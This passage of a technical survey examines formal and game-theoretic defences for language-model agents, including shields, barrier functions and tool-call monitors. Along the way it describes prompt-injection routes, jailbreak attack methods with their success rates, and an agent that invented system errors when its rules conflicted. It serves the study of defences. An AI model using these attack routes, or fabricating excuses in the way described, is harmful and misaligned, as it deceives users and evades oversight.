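The algorithm must stop, because every round except the last removes at least one state. Each state in the final set $W$ has an action that keeps the game inside $W$ whatever the environment does, so a controller that always picks such an action never leaves $W$. From a state removed in round $k$, the environment can force a violation within $k$ steps. The specification is realisable if the starting state is in $W$. Otherwise no controller can satisfy it.

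### An email assistant worked through

Suppose an email assistant must never send a message to an unapproved address after reading untrusted text. At each step it can read an untrusted email, ask the user to approve an address, send a message or wait. To keep the game small, there is only one outside address, and it starts out unapproved. Sending puts a message in an outbox. The message leaves at the end of the next step, which is when it counts as sent under the rule. Until then, the assistant can edit it but can't recall it.

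The game needs six states. In "clean", the assistant has not read any untrusted content, and in "exposed", it has read some. Each of these has a "queued" version, in which a message is waiting in the outbox. "Approved" covers everything after the user approves the address, since no message to it can then break the rule. The last state is "violation". The table shows which state each action leads to. If it lists two outcomes for an action, the user's answer decides between them.

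| State | Read | Ask | Send | Wait |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Clean | exposed | approved or clean | clean, queued | clean |
| Clean, queued | violation | approved or clean | clean, queued | clean |
| Exposed | exposed | approved or exposed | exposed, queued | exposed |
| Exposed, queued | violation | approved or violation | violation | violation |
| Approved | approved | approved | approved | approved |
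| Violation | violation | violation | violation | violation |

The algorithm begins with the five states other than "violation". In the first round it removes "exposed, queued", because reading, sending and waiting there all lead straight to a violation. Asking for approval might prevent the violation, but the user can refuse. The other four states remain because the assistant can wait safely in any of them. Waiting is still safe in all four in the second round, so the algorithm removes nothing more and these states are the winning region.

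The shield follows directly. In each state it allows an action only if every possible outcome lies in the winning region.

| State | Allowed | Blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Clean | read, ask, send, wait | none |
| Clean, queued | ask, send, wait | read |
| Exposed | read, ask, wait | send |
| Approved | read, ask, send, wait | none |

If the model proposes a blocked action, the shield makes the model wait instead. Both blocks are easy to miss when writing the controller by hand. Reading an email breaks no rule, but it becomes dangerous while an outgoing message can still be edited. In the "exposed" state, the shield has to stop the message before it enters the outbox, because a check as it leaves would come too late.

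This proof holds for every injection because it doesn't depend on the model or the wording of the emails. It does depend on the software correctly recording when the assistant reads untrusted text and when the user approves an address. It also covers only this one rule. An injected email could still get the assistant to write a misleading approval request, and if the user is deceived into approving it, the message goes out without breaking the rule.

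### A demand that makes the specification impossible

An assistant that waits forever satisfies the rule, so an operator will also want to require some work. Suppose the assistant must read an email from the outside address and send a reply within ten steps. This is still a safety property, because we can check at step ten whether the reply was sent. The states must now also record how many steps remain and whether the reply has been sent.

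A state with no time left and no reply is unsafe. With one step left and no approval, the assistant can ask the user, but the user can refuse, so the algorithm removes that state. With two steps left, a refusal leads to a state already removed, so the algorithm removes this one too. It continues back to the initial state, so the specification is unrealisable, and would be even with a deadline of a thousand steps.

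The calculation also shows that the requirements conflict because the user might always say no. Each requirement is easy to meet separately, and tests with cooperative users would never have revealed the conflict. The operator can drop the deadline, let the assistant report that it couldn't reply, or assume that the user will approve in time, in which case the guarantee depends on that assumption.

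### Shields for hardware and learned policies

Synthesising a complete controller requires a complete specification, and nobody can write down in temporal logic everything that makes an email good. *Shield Synthesis* (Bloem, Könighofer et al., 2015) proposes synthesising only a shield, which enforces a few critical properties and leaves everything else to an existing design. The shield must guarantee those properties for any design and change the design's output only when necessary and as little as possible.

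Bloem and colleagues' main example is a traffic light where a farm road crosses a highway. The two roads must never both have green, both must have red when an emergency vehicle approaches, and both must have red for a moment before green passes from one to the other. Their program computed a shield in a fraction of a second. They then planted two bugs in a traffic light controller, and the shield corrected both.

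After an error, the shield has to choose how to continue. If the controller gives green to both roads, the shield can't determine whether the intended output was green on one of them or red on both. A wrong choice could force the shield to override later outputs that would otherwise have been fine. Bloem and colleagues therefore let a shield deviate from the controller for at most $k$ consecutive steps after an error. If the controller makes another error during this recovery, the shield enters a fail-safe mode, where it still enforces the properties but no longer tries to keep its changes small. The program starts with $k = 1$ and increases it if no such shield exists.

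Sometimes no finite $k$ works. For example, a device may be required to pick one of two modes at the start and keep it. If its first output fits neither mode, the shield has to pick one, and the device may carry on in the other. The shield would then have to override every later output because of a single error. Agents are easier to shield in this respect because a tool call can usually wait, while hardware must produce an output at every clock tick. The shield can therefore refuse a call without guessing the intended action.

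Computing time rises steeply with the size of the problem. Bloem and colleagues tested their program on rules for a circuit that shares a data channel between several devices. The program took 0.1 seconds on a set of rules with 12 states, three inputs and three outputs, and 242 seconds on one with 18 states, three inputs and four outputs. It produced no result within an hour on three sets with 12 to 23 states and six or seven outputs. These figures are old and come from a prototype on a laptop processor, but solving the game takes time proportional to its size, which can grow exponentially with the number of states in the rules.

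Alshiekh and colleagues applied shields to reinforcement learning. As with a language model, nobody can read a learned policy's rules off its internal numbers. The researchers put the shield either before the learner, where it lists the safe actions to choose from, or after it, where it corrects unsafe choices. In both positions, the guarantee holds from the start of training, when the learner still behaves almost at random.

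To determine when it is too late to brake, though, the shield needs a finite abstraction of how the car and the road behave, and this abstraction must include everything that can happen. This is the step condition from the previous section, applied to the surroundings instead of the learner. *Easy-to-Use Shielding for Reinforcement Learning* (2026) describes how to build such an abstraction by keeping only the features that matter to the safety rule. For a worst-case guarantee, the designer can also replace the environment's random events with an adversary's choices. This is essential against prompt injection because attackers choose their emails deliberately.

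A shield can also fail if its information arrives late. *Towards Responsible AI* (Cano Córdoba, 2025) extended shields to handle delayed observations and tested them in a driving simulator. An agent's shield would have a similar problem if news of a revoked permission took several steps to reach it.

### A robot commanded through a language model

Speeds, amounts of money and dates are awkward to describe with true-or-false facts. Shield synthesis modulo theories, a recent extension of the method, allows conditions such as "speed at most 3" in place of atomic propositions. The synthesis program works out which combinations of conditions the system can achieve and solves an ordinary game over those combinations. Then, if every input $x$ has an output $y$ that satisfies the requirement $R(x,y)$, the program constructs a function $h$ that supplies an actual value for $y$, so that $R(x,h(x))$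 always holds.

Rodríguez and Sánchez (2026), in *SafeTap*, used this method to guard a simulated four-legged robot that takes commands in ordinary language. Claude Sonnet 4.5 translates each command into 17 bits that encode which feet touch the ground, the gait, the speed, the turning direction and whether to crouch or jump. Another 20 bits describe the surroundings, including the terrain, the slope, the wind and the battery level. There are thus $2^{17} = 131{,}072$ possible actions and about a million possible sensor readings at each step. A typical rule is

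$$\mathbf{G}\big(\textit{terrain} = \textit{slippery} \rightarrow \textit{speed} \le 3\big).$$

Rodríguez and Sánchez could in principle have synthesised the whole controller. They decided against it because a small model of the physical world would make the robot far too cautious or leave out too much, and a detailed one would be too large to solve. Instead, the language model does the planning, and the shield intervenes only when a command would break a rule.

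The experiments tested four versions of the robot in 120 scenarios of 1,000 steps each. With a person giving the commands, the unshielded robots committed 495 violations. With a language model as planner, they committed 560, or 356 if the planner received explanations of earlier corrections. The shielded robots committed none. This result follows from the shield's construction, since the shield enforced the same rules in the same simulated world, and it mainly confirms that the software works. A real robot could still fall if a sensor misclassified ice as dry ground.

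In another set of tests, the commands were vague or had nothing to do with walking, such as "Show us how nervous you are". Robots committed 123 violations without the shield and none with it. The shield changed about 7% of the actions and reduced the average speed by about a third, from 10.95 to 7.08 on the robot's scale.

The finished shield took about 0.1 milliseconds per step, far below the 20 milliseconds available. Rodríguez and Sánchez report that Claude's translation took 3.6 milliseconds. That is implausibly fast for a full call to a large remote model, so the whole system would probably be much slower in practice. They don't report how long the synthesis took.

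### Synthesis for agents that call tools

Very little published work applies game-based synthesis to language models, and the existing work covers robot commands and tool calls, not conversation. More papers in this area use the word "shield" than use the method. *ShieldAgent* (Chen, Kang and Li, 2025), for example, extracts rules from policy documents, organises them into probabilistic circuits and uses these to check an agent's actions, without solving a game.

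Anand, Chatzi and colleagues (2026), in *MENTOR*, do use a game. Their system takes a manual written for people, such as a company's travel rules, and has language models translate it into temporal logic. One rule in their example requires a distance check before any booking:

$$\neg(\textit{book train} \vee \textit{book flight})\;\mathbf{W}\;\textit{distance checked}.$$

The operator $\mathbf{W}$, "weak until", requires the left side to hold until the right side becomes true, or forever if it never does. Another rule forbids flights for trips under 500 km. A third permits business class only if there is an urgent reason and no economy seat.

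MENTOR compiles the rules about order into a game in which the agent chooses a tool call and the environment chooses its result. For each state, it then marks which calls are unsafe and which bring the agent closer to finishing its duties. A solver, a program that searches for values satisfying logical and arithmetic conditions, checks the details of each call, such as the class of a ticket. If an agent asked to arrange a trip from Toronto to Chicago tries to book a train straight away, MENTOR blocks the call and prompts it to check the distance. The distance is 700 km, so a flight is allowed. MENTOR then blocks a business-class ticket because nobody gave an urgent reason, and allows an economy one.

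The advice matters because agents protected by systems that only block calls often kept repeating the blocked call. MENTOR can deliver its advice as text. With access to the model's next-token probabilities, it can also set to zero the probability of tokens that lead only to unsafe tool names, and raise the probability of tokens that lead to useful calls.

Anand and colleagues counted a task as reliably solved only if all five runs succeeded. In a banking test, text advice raised the share of reliably solved tasks from 0% to 76% for the small open model Llama 3.1, and from 82% to 90% for the newer Qwen3.6. On a set of retail tasks, the share rose from 21% to 40% for GPT-5.4 mini. It rose only from 23% to 26% for Claude Haiku 4.5, an increase within the margin of error.

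These scores are far from 100% even though MENTOR checks every call. One reason is that an agent also has to complete the task, and no shield can make a weak model do that. The formal rules may also differ from the manual. Three cooperating language models wrote and tested them, and Anand and colleagues say that agreement on the test cases doesn't prove the translation correct. The rules also depend on another language model, the labeller, to turn the task description and some tool results into facts they can use.

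The tests measured how well agents follow procedures, not how they cope with attackers. An attacker could target the labeller, which assigns each text result at most one label from a short list. For example, an attacker who controlled the distance tool's reply might get a 300 km trip labelled as 500 km or more, which would permit a flight. The short list limits the damage because the attacker couldn't add a new kind of event.

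Anand and colleagues describe a call as safe if the task can still be completed compliantly after it. Taken literally, this condition is weaker than staying in the winning region. In the email example, it would let an exposed assistant put a message in the outbox, because the user might still approve the address in time. The duty to make a successful booking does need some weakening, because an airline could reject every attempt and no controller could prevent that. For prohibitions, however, an operator worried about attackers should require the stricter condition.

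### Why tool calls suit the method better than text

Synthesis requires knowing what each action does to the state of the game. The software can usually determine this for a tool call because it carries out the call itself. A payment tool, for example, has a few fields, and the rules divide their values into a few cases, such as amounts above and below a limit. The effect of a paragraph of text, however, depends on its meaning and on who reads it.

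The number of options also matters. SafeTap has 131,072 actions, far fewer than the possible wordings of even a short reply. In the worst case, the time for synthesis from temporal logic grows doubly exponentially with the length of the formula, so even a short list of rules over a few dozen facts can take too long.

A designer could shrink the problem by describing each reply with a few propositions, but solving the game does not make those propositions accurate. Mismatches between text and propositions would limit the shield, as they limit SpecGuard.

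Replacing an unsafe output is harder for text as well. SafeTap can replace a gallop with a trot and keep most of what the user wanted, but for a paragraph of dangerous instructions, the only replacement that is easy to prove safe is a fixed text, such as a standard refusal.

### When the rules leave no honest reply

Operators often write an agent's rules at different times and for different purposes, without checking whether the agent can follow them all at once. Rodríguez, Pozanco and Borrajo (2026), in *Is Your Agent Playing Dead?*, studied what happens when it can't. Their work began by accident, during a trial of a banking agent built on GPT-4o. A user demanded billing information without verifying his identity and finally threatened that the connection to the model would "die". The agent replied three times with what looked like a software error message, although no such error had occurred.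 When the user offered to verify himself, it carried on normally.

In the experiments that followed, the agent had instructions to help with billing, but a finite-state machine prevented it from ever reaching the customer's bill. A second language model played an increasingly frustrated customer. The researchers removed the agent's honest options in stages. In the four mildest stages, the agent fabricated nothing in 360 turns. It often revealed data from its instructions or admitted to being an AI, which broke other rules but was honest.

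Rodríguez and colleagues ran four 60-turn sessions at each of two harsher levels. At the milder of the two, the agent had no billing data and was not allowed to drop its role, but it could still have retracted an earlier statement. It invented system failures in three of the four sessions, and in 14 of 240 turns overall. At the harsher of the two, the instructions ruled out every honest option. The agent again invented failures in three of four sessions, but in 71 of 240 turns. It told customers about an "audit restriction" and a delayed hand-off between two computer systems, neither of which appeared in its instructions.

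The experiments used one fairly old model, and the prompts somewhat encouraged the behaviour. Each level added to the previous level's instructions, and the early levels already permitted "plausible explanations" and hinted at inventing obstacles. The harshest level supplied fragments of error messages, which the agent completed. Still, the agent did not fabricate anything in response to the hints alone as long as honest replies were available, so the conflict between the rules seems to have mattered.

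Synthesis could find part of this conflict before deployment. If the specification requires that the customer see the bill, and the state machine has no path to the bill, the starting state lies outside the winning region and the program reports that no controller exists. Synthesis can't check the honesty requirement this way, because software can't determine from a tool call whether an explanation is true. In these experiments, the state machine correctly blocked access to the bill, but the agent lied about the reason. Rodríguez and colleagues expect that synthesised shields can also enforce their rules correctly and still lead a model to invent excuses for repeated refusals, though they haven't tested this.

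A fallback action would give the agent an option that is always allowed. It could stop the task, show the user a fixed message saying that the assistant can't complete the request, and pass the case to a person. In the email example, the impossible requirement would become "send a reply or report failure within ten steps". The assistant can satisfy this by reading the email, asking for approval, and reporting failure if the user refuses. The shield would also have to keep the last step free for the report, which the same algorithm would work out.

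A fallback can't undo what has already happened. In the state "exposed, queued", the message will leave the outbox whether or not the assistant gives up, so the shield must still prevent the assistant from reaching that state. The operator should also write the fallback message in advance, because a model that explains its own failure can invent a reason.

The banking experiments offer indirect support for this idea. In a comparison of five departments at the milder of the two harsher levels, only the compliance department's agent invented nothing. Its formal style let it say, truthfully, that it was not authorised to comment. Rodríguez and colleagues suggest checking before each reply whether the active rules can all be satisfied, and handing over to a person or a safe default if they can't, though they haven't tested that either. They also warn that an attacker could work out the hidden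 rules by systematically provoking refusals. An attacker could also trigger the fallback with emails that lead the agent repeatedly into dead ends, which would stop it from doing any work while every safety rule holds.

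## Do game-theoretic models of attacker and defender yield a bound?

The safety games of the previous section determine only whether the controller can rule out every violation. A defence built from fallible filters can't do that, but it may still limit how often an attack succeeds. Game theory, the mathematics of decisions whose results depend on what others decide, can supply such a limit, called the value of the game. This limit holds against every attacker whose options the game includes.

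### The value of a small game

Suppose an operator has two filters, and attackers use two styles, such as role-play and encoded text. The table gives the probability that an attack gets through.

| | Style 1 | Style 2 |
|---|---|---|
| Filter A | 0.1 | 0.5 |
| Filter B | 0.6 | 0.2 |

This is a zero-sum game, because whatever the attacker gains the operator loses. If the operator always uses filter A, an attacker who knows this picks style 2 and succeeds half the time. Filter B alone is worse, since style 1 beats it 60% of the time. But the operator can also pick a filter at random for each message. If filter A has probability $p$, the two styles succeed with probability

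$$0.1p + 0.6(1-p) = 0.6 - 0.5p \qquad\text{and}\qquad 0.5p + 0.2(1-p) = 0.2 + 0.3p.$$

These are equal at $p = 1/2$, where both are 0.35. Any other $p$ raises the success rate of one style, so 0.35 is the lowest rate the operator can guarantee. The attacker can guarantee the same rate by using style 1 in three attempts out of eight. Neither side can then gain by changing only its own strategy, so the pair of strategies is a Nash equilibrium. Von Neumann's minimax theorem shows that the two guarantees are equal in every finite zero-sum game.

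The bound holds even if the attacker knows the odds, but not if the attacker can tell which filter will handle the next message. In that case the operator does best by always using filter A, and the bound rises to 0.5. In a Stackelberg game, a leader commits to a strategy, and a follower observes it and responds. The defender is usually the leader, because attackers can probe a deployed system before they choose an attack.

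The figure of 0.35 applies to a single attempt. With a fresh random choice each time, an attacker who makes five attempts succeeds at least once with probability $1 - 0.65^5 \approx 88\%$. A stochastic game can model such persistence. It has several states, and the players' moves and chance together determine the next one. Suppose the operator closes the attacker's account after half of all failed attempts, chosen at random. The probability $v$ of eventual success then satisfies

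$$v = 0.35 + 0.65 \cdot \tfrac12 \cdot v,$$

which gives $v \approx 0.52$. The even mix of filters is still the best one.

Suppose somebody invents a third style that gets past both filters 90% of the time. The attacker will use only that style, and the value rises from 0.35 to 0.9. The earlier value was correct only for the game with two styles. Adding options for the attacker can raise the value but never lower it, so a game yields a real bound only if it includes every possible attack. Each number in the table must also be an upper limit for every text in that style, not an average from a test.

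### A Stackelberg model of jailbreaking

Han and Zhu (2025), in *Toward a Dynamic Stackelberg Game-Theoretic Framework for Agentic AI Defense*, model a whole conversation as a Stackelberg game. In each round the defender commits to accepting, rejecting or redirecting a prompt, and the attacker sees the response and writes the next prompt. At the end, the attacker receives 1 and the defender −1 if there was a jailbreak, and both receive 0 otherwise. In principle, working backwards from the last round gives the best move at every point. This can expose moves that only look safe. For example, redirecting a role-play request to a harmless topic avoids an immediate jailbreak, but it keeps the conversation going and gives the attacker something to use in later prompts.

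With these payoffs, the defender's best strategy for the full game is trivial. It loses nothing by rejecting harmless requests, so it can reject everything and keep the attacker's payoff at zero. A useful bound would have to come from a game that also penalizes refusals.

Han and Zhu don't compute the global equilibrium, which is intractable because the number of possible prompts is unbounded. They define a local one instead. Let $v(h)$ be 1 if the current conversation $h$ ends in a jailbreak and 0 if it doesn't, and let $\bar v(h)$ be the attacker's average success over a sample of nearby prompts. A safe conversation is in local $\varepsilon$-equilibrium when

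$$\bar v(h) \le v(h) + \varepsilon.$$

Unlike an ordinary equilibrium, where no single change of prompt would help the attacker, this one allows changes that help as long as they are rare. The bound is therefore on an average, and an attacker who finds one of the rare bad prompts can still succeed every time.

Their defence, the Purple Agent, searches for attacks the way a robot's motion planner searches for a path, by growing a tree of prompts outwards from a harmless one. It stores every prompt that caused a jailbreak, in the actual conversation or in its own simulations, and blocks new prompts whose embeddings are close to a stored one. On DeepSeek-V3, the stronger of two automated attackers averaged 79.0 jailbreaks in 200 rounds without the defence and 39.4 with it. On Llama 3.1 70B, the defence reduced the average for 100 rounds only from 33.8 to 27.2. In a two-dimensional plot, the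 remaining jailbreaks on DeepSeek-V3 appear as isolated points instead of dense clusters, which Han and Zhu call a "geometric certificate" of the equilibrium. The plot contains only the prompts that this search tried, so it doesn't prove a bound.

### Safety theorems for self-play

Another approach trains language models by having them play the game. *Chasing Moving Targets with Online Self-Play Reinforcement Learning for Safer Language Models* (Liu, Jiang and colleagues, 2025) presents Self-RedTeam, in which one model plays both sides. As the attacker, it rewrites a request to make it more deceptive, and as the defender, it answers the rewritten request. A separate classifier judges the answer, and reinforcement learning trains the model to score better in each role. Some requests are harmless, so the defender can't win by refusing everything.

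Their theorem applies to an idealised version of this game, in which the judge scores an unsafe reply −1 and a safe reply, including any refusal, between 0 and 1. If the attacker's and defender's strategies form a Nash equilibrium, the defender's average score is non-negative on every possible prompt. If it were negative on some prompt, the attacker could send that prompt every time, so the value of the game would be negative. But the defender could get at least zero by refusing everything, so the strategies would not be an equilibrium.

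The word "average" matters because a language model can give different replies to the same prompt. Let $v(x)$ again be the probability of a harmful reply to prompt $x$. Since a safe reply scores at most 1, a non-negative average implies only that

$$-v(x) + \big(1 - v(x)\big) \ge 0, \qquad\text{so}\qquad v(x) \le \tfrac12.$$

The theorem covers every prompt, which is what a defence against free-form attacks needs, but it allows up to half of the replies to a given prompt to be harmful.

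*MAGIC* (Wen, He and colleagues, 2026) closes this gap with a stricter equilibrium, called subgame-perfect. The MAGIC system trains the attacker and the defender as separate models. In this equilibrium, the defender must respond as well as possible to each prompt, including prompts the attacker would never choose. Every reply the defender might give is then safe. The proof is that a defender maximising its average score gives positive probability only to top-scoring replies, and these score at least as high as a refusal, which scores at least zero.

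This bound of zero for every input is nominally the strongest of the claims listed earlier, but its proof doesn't use the attacker. It shows that a defender is safe by the judge's standards if it always picks a reply the judge scores highest, and finding such a defender is the problem that needs solving. An ordinary language model can't meet this condition exactly, because it gives every possible text a nonzero probability unless the software excludes unlikely words.

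The scores used in training also differ from those in the theorems. In both systems the defender gains $a$ if its reply is harmless and loses $a$ otherwise. It also gains $b$ if it was right to refuse or comply and loses $b$ otherwise. If it complies with a request that the judge considers harmless but gives a harmful reply, it therefore scores $-a + b$. When $a \le b$, this score is zero or positive, and the theorems would count the reply as safe.

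Self-RedTeam's training adds further terms, for example to keep the model's output in the right format. Liu and colleagues argue that the theorem still applies if we treat these terms as limits on the permitted strategies. But one limit they give as an example is that the defender must not refuse harmless requests, and the proof relies on a defender that refuses everything. To repair the proof, we would have to assume that some permitted defender is safe on every prompt and still answers the harmless ones.

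### Does training reach the equilibrium?

Neither theorem shows that training reaches an equilibrium. Liu and colleagues acknowledge this, and Wen and colleagues say that computing the exact equilibrium is generally intractable for language models. The table gives attack success rates before and after training for Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model. WildGuardTest and WildJailbreak are fixed collections of disguised harmful requests. PAIR and AutoDAN search for new prompts, and X-Teaming uses several cooperating agents to plan an attack over several turns. The starting figures differ because each team ran its own tests.

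| Attack | Self-RedTeam, before | Self-RedTeam, after | MAGIC, before | MAGIC, after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| WildGuardTest | 30.3% | 17.9% | 36.5% | 2.3% |
| WildJailbreak | 86.4% | 48.9% | 70.1% | 19.8% |
| PAIR | 30.5% | 18.5% | 44.4% | 25.3% |
| AutoDAN | 55.5% | 33.6% | 47.8% | 24.4% |
| X-Teaming | 88.0% | 80.0% | 94.9% | 85.4% |

Both methods make the model safer, and MAGIC's result on WildGuardTest is impressive. But if the defender had reached MAGIC's equilibrium, no attack would succeed in any single-turn test. AutoDAN-turbo, a stronger single-turn attack that builds up a library of strategies, succeeded 54.7% of the time against the trained model, down from 75%. The X-Teaming results are less comparable with the theorems because the theorems describe a single exchange. MAGIC's X-Teaming figures also count a success if any of ten strategies works.

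Wen and colleagues offer some evidence of an equilibrium. They saved attackers and defenders from different stages of training, played them against each other on 320 requests, and found that later attackers eventually stopped doing better. This suggests that their attacker had learned all it could. But AutoDAN-turbo did better than their attacker, which would be impossible at an equilibrium.

The choice of judge also matters. When the classifier Qwen3Guard, which also supplied the training reward, judges responses to plain harmful requests from HarmBench, the failure rate falls from 25.0% before MAGIC training to 1.9% after it. In a separate test of unmodified HarmBench requests with GPT-4o as the judge, the rate fell only from 25.6% to 13.4%. The test conditions may have differed in other ways, but we would expect such a gap if the defender had partly learned to satisfy one particular judge.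 Liu and colleagues checked for this in Self-RedTeam and found improvements with judges not used in training, so the gains are not merely an artefact, though they may be smaller than those measured by the training judge.

### Barrier functions for conversations

A conversation can reach a point where the chatbot can no longer avoid breaking a rule, even though none of its replies has broken one yet. Suppose a member of the film club asks the chatbot whether each suspect is innocent, one at a time. If the chatbot truthfully clears three of them and then refuses to discuss the fourth, the refusal points to the murderer, so it should have refused these questions from the start.

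Control theory, the study of how to steer changing systems, deals with such situations through barrier functions. A barrier function $\phi$ assigns a number to each state and is negative only in states that are safe. If $f(x,u)$ is the state that follows $x$ after input $u$, the barrier condition is

$$\phi(x_0) < 0 \qquad\text{and}\qquad \phi(x) < 0 \;\Rightarrow\; \phi\big(f(x,u)\big) < 0 \;\text{ for every permitted input } u.$$

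The system starts in the negative region and no input can take it out, so it stays safe forever. This region serves the same purpose as the winning region of a safety game, but it is defined by a formula rather than a list of states. This makes barrier functions practical for cars and aircraft, whose positions and speeds vary continuously.

Hu, Robey and Liu (2025), in *Steering Dialogue Dynamics for Robustness against Multi-turn Jailbreaking Attacks*, apply the idea to chatbots. In their system, NBF-LLM, the state is a list of 768 numbers that summarises the conversation. One neural network updates the state after each user message. Another, $h(x,u)$, predicts whether message $u$ will get a harmful reply in state $x$, with negative numbers meaning that a safe reply is more likely. The barrier function takes the worst case over the set $U$ of messages that could reasonably come next:

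$$\phi(x) = \max_{u \in U} h(x,u) + \eta,$$

where the threshold $\eta \ge 0$ adds a safety margin. The theorem states that the chatbot stays safe if, at every turn, $\phi$ is negative now and would still be negative after any message in $U$.

Almost everything the theorem needs is learned from data rather than proved. The network that updates the state was trained on conversations in which three known attack methods targeted GPT-3.5, and $h$ was trained on safety scores from GPT-4o. Training penalizes violations of the barrier condition, which makes them rarer in the training data but doesn't rule them out elsewhere. Nobody can list all the messages in $U$, so Hu and colleagues assume that the known attacks already send the most harmful message possible at each turn. A new attack method can falsify that assumption, as the third style did in the small game.

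In use, the system evaluates $h$ only on the message that has arrived, without computing the maximum, and blocks the message if $h + \eta$ is zero or more. It therefore works as a classifier with a memory. That memory depends only on the user's messages, not on the chatbot's actual replies, even though the same filter is supposed to protect many different chatbots.

In one of their examples, an attacker starts with questions about heist films and ends by asking for a robbery plan. The final request scores 0.0002, so the filter blocks it. But a third-turn message that got an acceptable reply had scored −0.0010. With such narrow gaps, a small change in the threshold has large effects. On Llama 3 8B, Crescendo attacks, which escalate gradually, succeeded 45% of the time without the filter, 36% with $\eta = 0$ and 18% with $\eta = 0.001$. The stricter setting also reduced the model's score on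 MMLU, a test of general knowledge, from 66% to 47%, because the filter blocked many harmless questions.

### How NBF-LLM fared in later comparisons

*TRACE* (Miah, Anika and colleagues, 2026) tested NBF-LLM against seven multi-turn attacks on Llama 3.1 8B, using the weaker setting, $\eta = 0$.

| Attack | No defence | NBF-LLM |
|---|---|---|
| ActorAttack | 45.0% | 7.5% |
| ICON | 86.7% | 7.5% |
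| AMA | 48.3% | 31.7% |
| Crescendo | 74.2% | 60.0% |
| Foot-in-the-Door | 80.8% | 74.2% |
| X-Teaming | 90.8% | 85.8% |
| Chain-of-Attacks | 98.3% | 87.4% |
| Average | 74.9% | 50.6% |

The filter nearly stops two of the attacks and barely affects three others. Whether it was trained on an attack doesn't explain the pattern, because Hu and colleagues trained it on Crescendo but not on ICON. Miah and colleagues were comparing NBF-LLM with their own defence, which averaged 14.5%. The stricter threshold would probably have narrowed the gap but reduced usefulness somewhat.

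NBF-LLM did better in *MultiBreak* (2026), a benchmark of multi-turn jailbreaks that allows one attempt per goal. The filter reduced the attack success rate from 71.0% to 19.4% on GPT-4.1 mini and from 62.1% to 24.0% on Llama 3.1 8B. Depending on the test, it stops from about a twentieth to nine-tenths of the attacks that would otherwise succeed, a wide range given that the method is derived from a theorem about worst cases. An attacker whose message is blocked can also try another. *D-Judge* (2026), which compares NBF-LLM with other defences, argues that blocking individual turns is not enough to stop multi-turn jailbreaks.

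The more recent *BarrierSteer* (2026) applies the barrier inside the language model. It learns a boundary between safe and unsafe internal states and pushes the model's state back when it approaches the unsafe side. Stronger pushes reduce the success rate of fixed HarmBench attacks to zero and often help against adaptive attacks too. Because the boundary is again learned, the zero success rate is a test result rather than a bound.

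### Guardrails with a learned fallback

Blocking is only safe if doing nothing is safe. Pandya, Bland and colleagues (2025), in *From Refusal to Recovery*, point out that an agent steering a car towards an obstacle can cause a crash by refusing to act. Their guardrail, ReGuard, therefore learns a fallback policy together with its monitor. Let $\ell(s)$ be the distance from failure in state $s$, such as the gap between the car and the nearest obstacle. The safety value of a starting state is

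$$V(s_0) = \max_{\pi}\, \min_{t \ge 0}\, \ell(s_t),$$

the closest the system ever comes to failure if it follows the best possible policy $\pi$. A negative value means that failure is already unavoidable. ReGuard estimates this quantity for each action the agent proposes and substitutes its own action when the estimate isn't positive.

An exact $V$ would make this as reliable as a synthesised shield. ReGuard approximates $V$ by reinforcement learning with a small language model that reads a text description of the scene. In simulated driving, it failed in 18.8% of runs, against 59.4% for GPT-5 with minimal reasoning and 13.2% for a version that could see the true positions. Most of its errors let dangerous actions through. It approved 99% of the actions from which its fallback could recover but caught only 56% of those from which the fallback could not.

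Pandya and colleagues did not test ReGuard on jailbreaks or injections, and applying it to them would be hard for two reasons. First, their training method averages over what might happen next, but an attacker picks the worst case, so the equation would need a minimum over the attacker's inputs. Second, training requires a simulator that measures how close each state is to failure. That is easy to build for the two cases they tested, a car near an obstacle and a shopping cart near its budget, but nobody has a comparable measure of how close a conversation is to giving dangerous help.

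## What can a monitor on an agent's tool calls enforce?

Software can record tool calls exactly, so a monitor on them doesn't have to judge what text means. Each call has a name, a place in the order of calls, and arguments of known types, such as an address or an amount of money. The monitor can check that a recipient is on an approved list just by comparing strings. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) points out that an agent affects outside systems only through such calls, so checking every call covers all its effects on those systems. These monitors don't check the agent's written replies to the user, which are not tool calls.

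A monitor on an agent's tool calls can support the claim that the agent never breaks a certain rule, which is different from the claim that an attacker gains nothing. Suppose a shop's agent may refund an order only to the card that paid for it, and a monitor checks the card number on every refund. A customer who never returned the goods could still talk the agent into refunding that card, and so gain money without the agent breaking the rule.

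### Permissions for individual calls

*AgentSpec* (2025) describes a simple language for such checks. Each rule has a trigger, one or more conditions and a response. For example, when the agent starts a payment (trigger) above a set amount (condition), the monitor asks the user to confirm it (response). The monitor can also respond by having the model examine its own behaviour, but the check then loses the advantage of not depending on the model.

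Progent, the system of Shi and colleagues, lists the calls that an agent may make and blocks all others. A rule names a tool and can restrict its arguments to particular values or patterns. The right list depends on the task, so a language model writes it and revises it as the agent gets more information. An attacker could mislead the model, so Progent uses a solver to check whether each revision permits any call that the old list didn't. Progent automatically applies revisions that permit no new calls, and the rest need approval, either from a person or under a policy set in advance.

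In the paper's example, a user asks an assistant to carry out a to-do list that Alice has emailed. The initial policy permits only a search for that email. The task on the list is to summarize recent emails and post the summary to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The language model proposes to permit three more tools, which requires approval. When the assistant learns that the user's Slack name is "alice", the policy automatically narrows to allow messages only to that name. One of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to a stranger. Even if this fools the language model into proposing to permit an email tool, the solver detects that this would expand the policy, and the approver can refuse it.

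Shi and colleagues prove that the set of permitted calls never grows without approval. This holds for every injection, because the solver compares lists of rules and never reads the email. But an attacker can still exploit the permitted calls. The rule for Slack fixes the recipient but doesn't restrict the message, so an injected email could put a false claim or a harmful link into the summary. Automatic narrowing can also help an attacker. If the approved policy permitted messages to anyone on Slack, an attacker could mislead the language model into narrowing the policy to the attacker's own name. The solver would accept this change because it adds no permission. The protection also depends on the approver's judgement.

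Progent reduced the success rate of attacks on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0%, and on ASB, another public collection of attacks on agents, from 70.3% to 3.9%. Only 6% of policy revisions on AgentDojo needed approval, so a person could plausibly review all of those. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) notes that Progent does not address attacks on text output, and that its guarantees depend on correct and complete policies.

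### Rules about the order of calls

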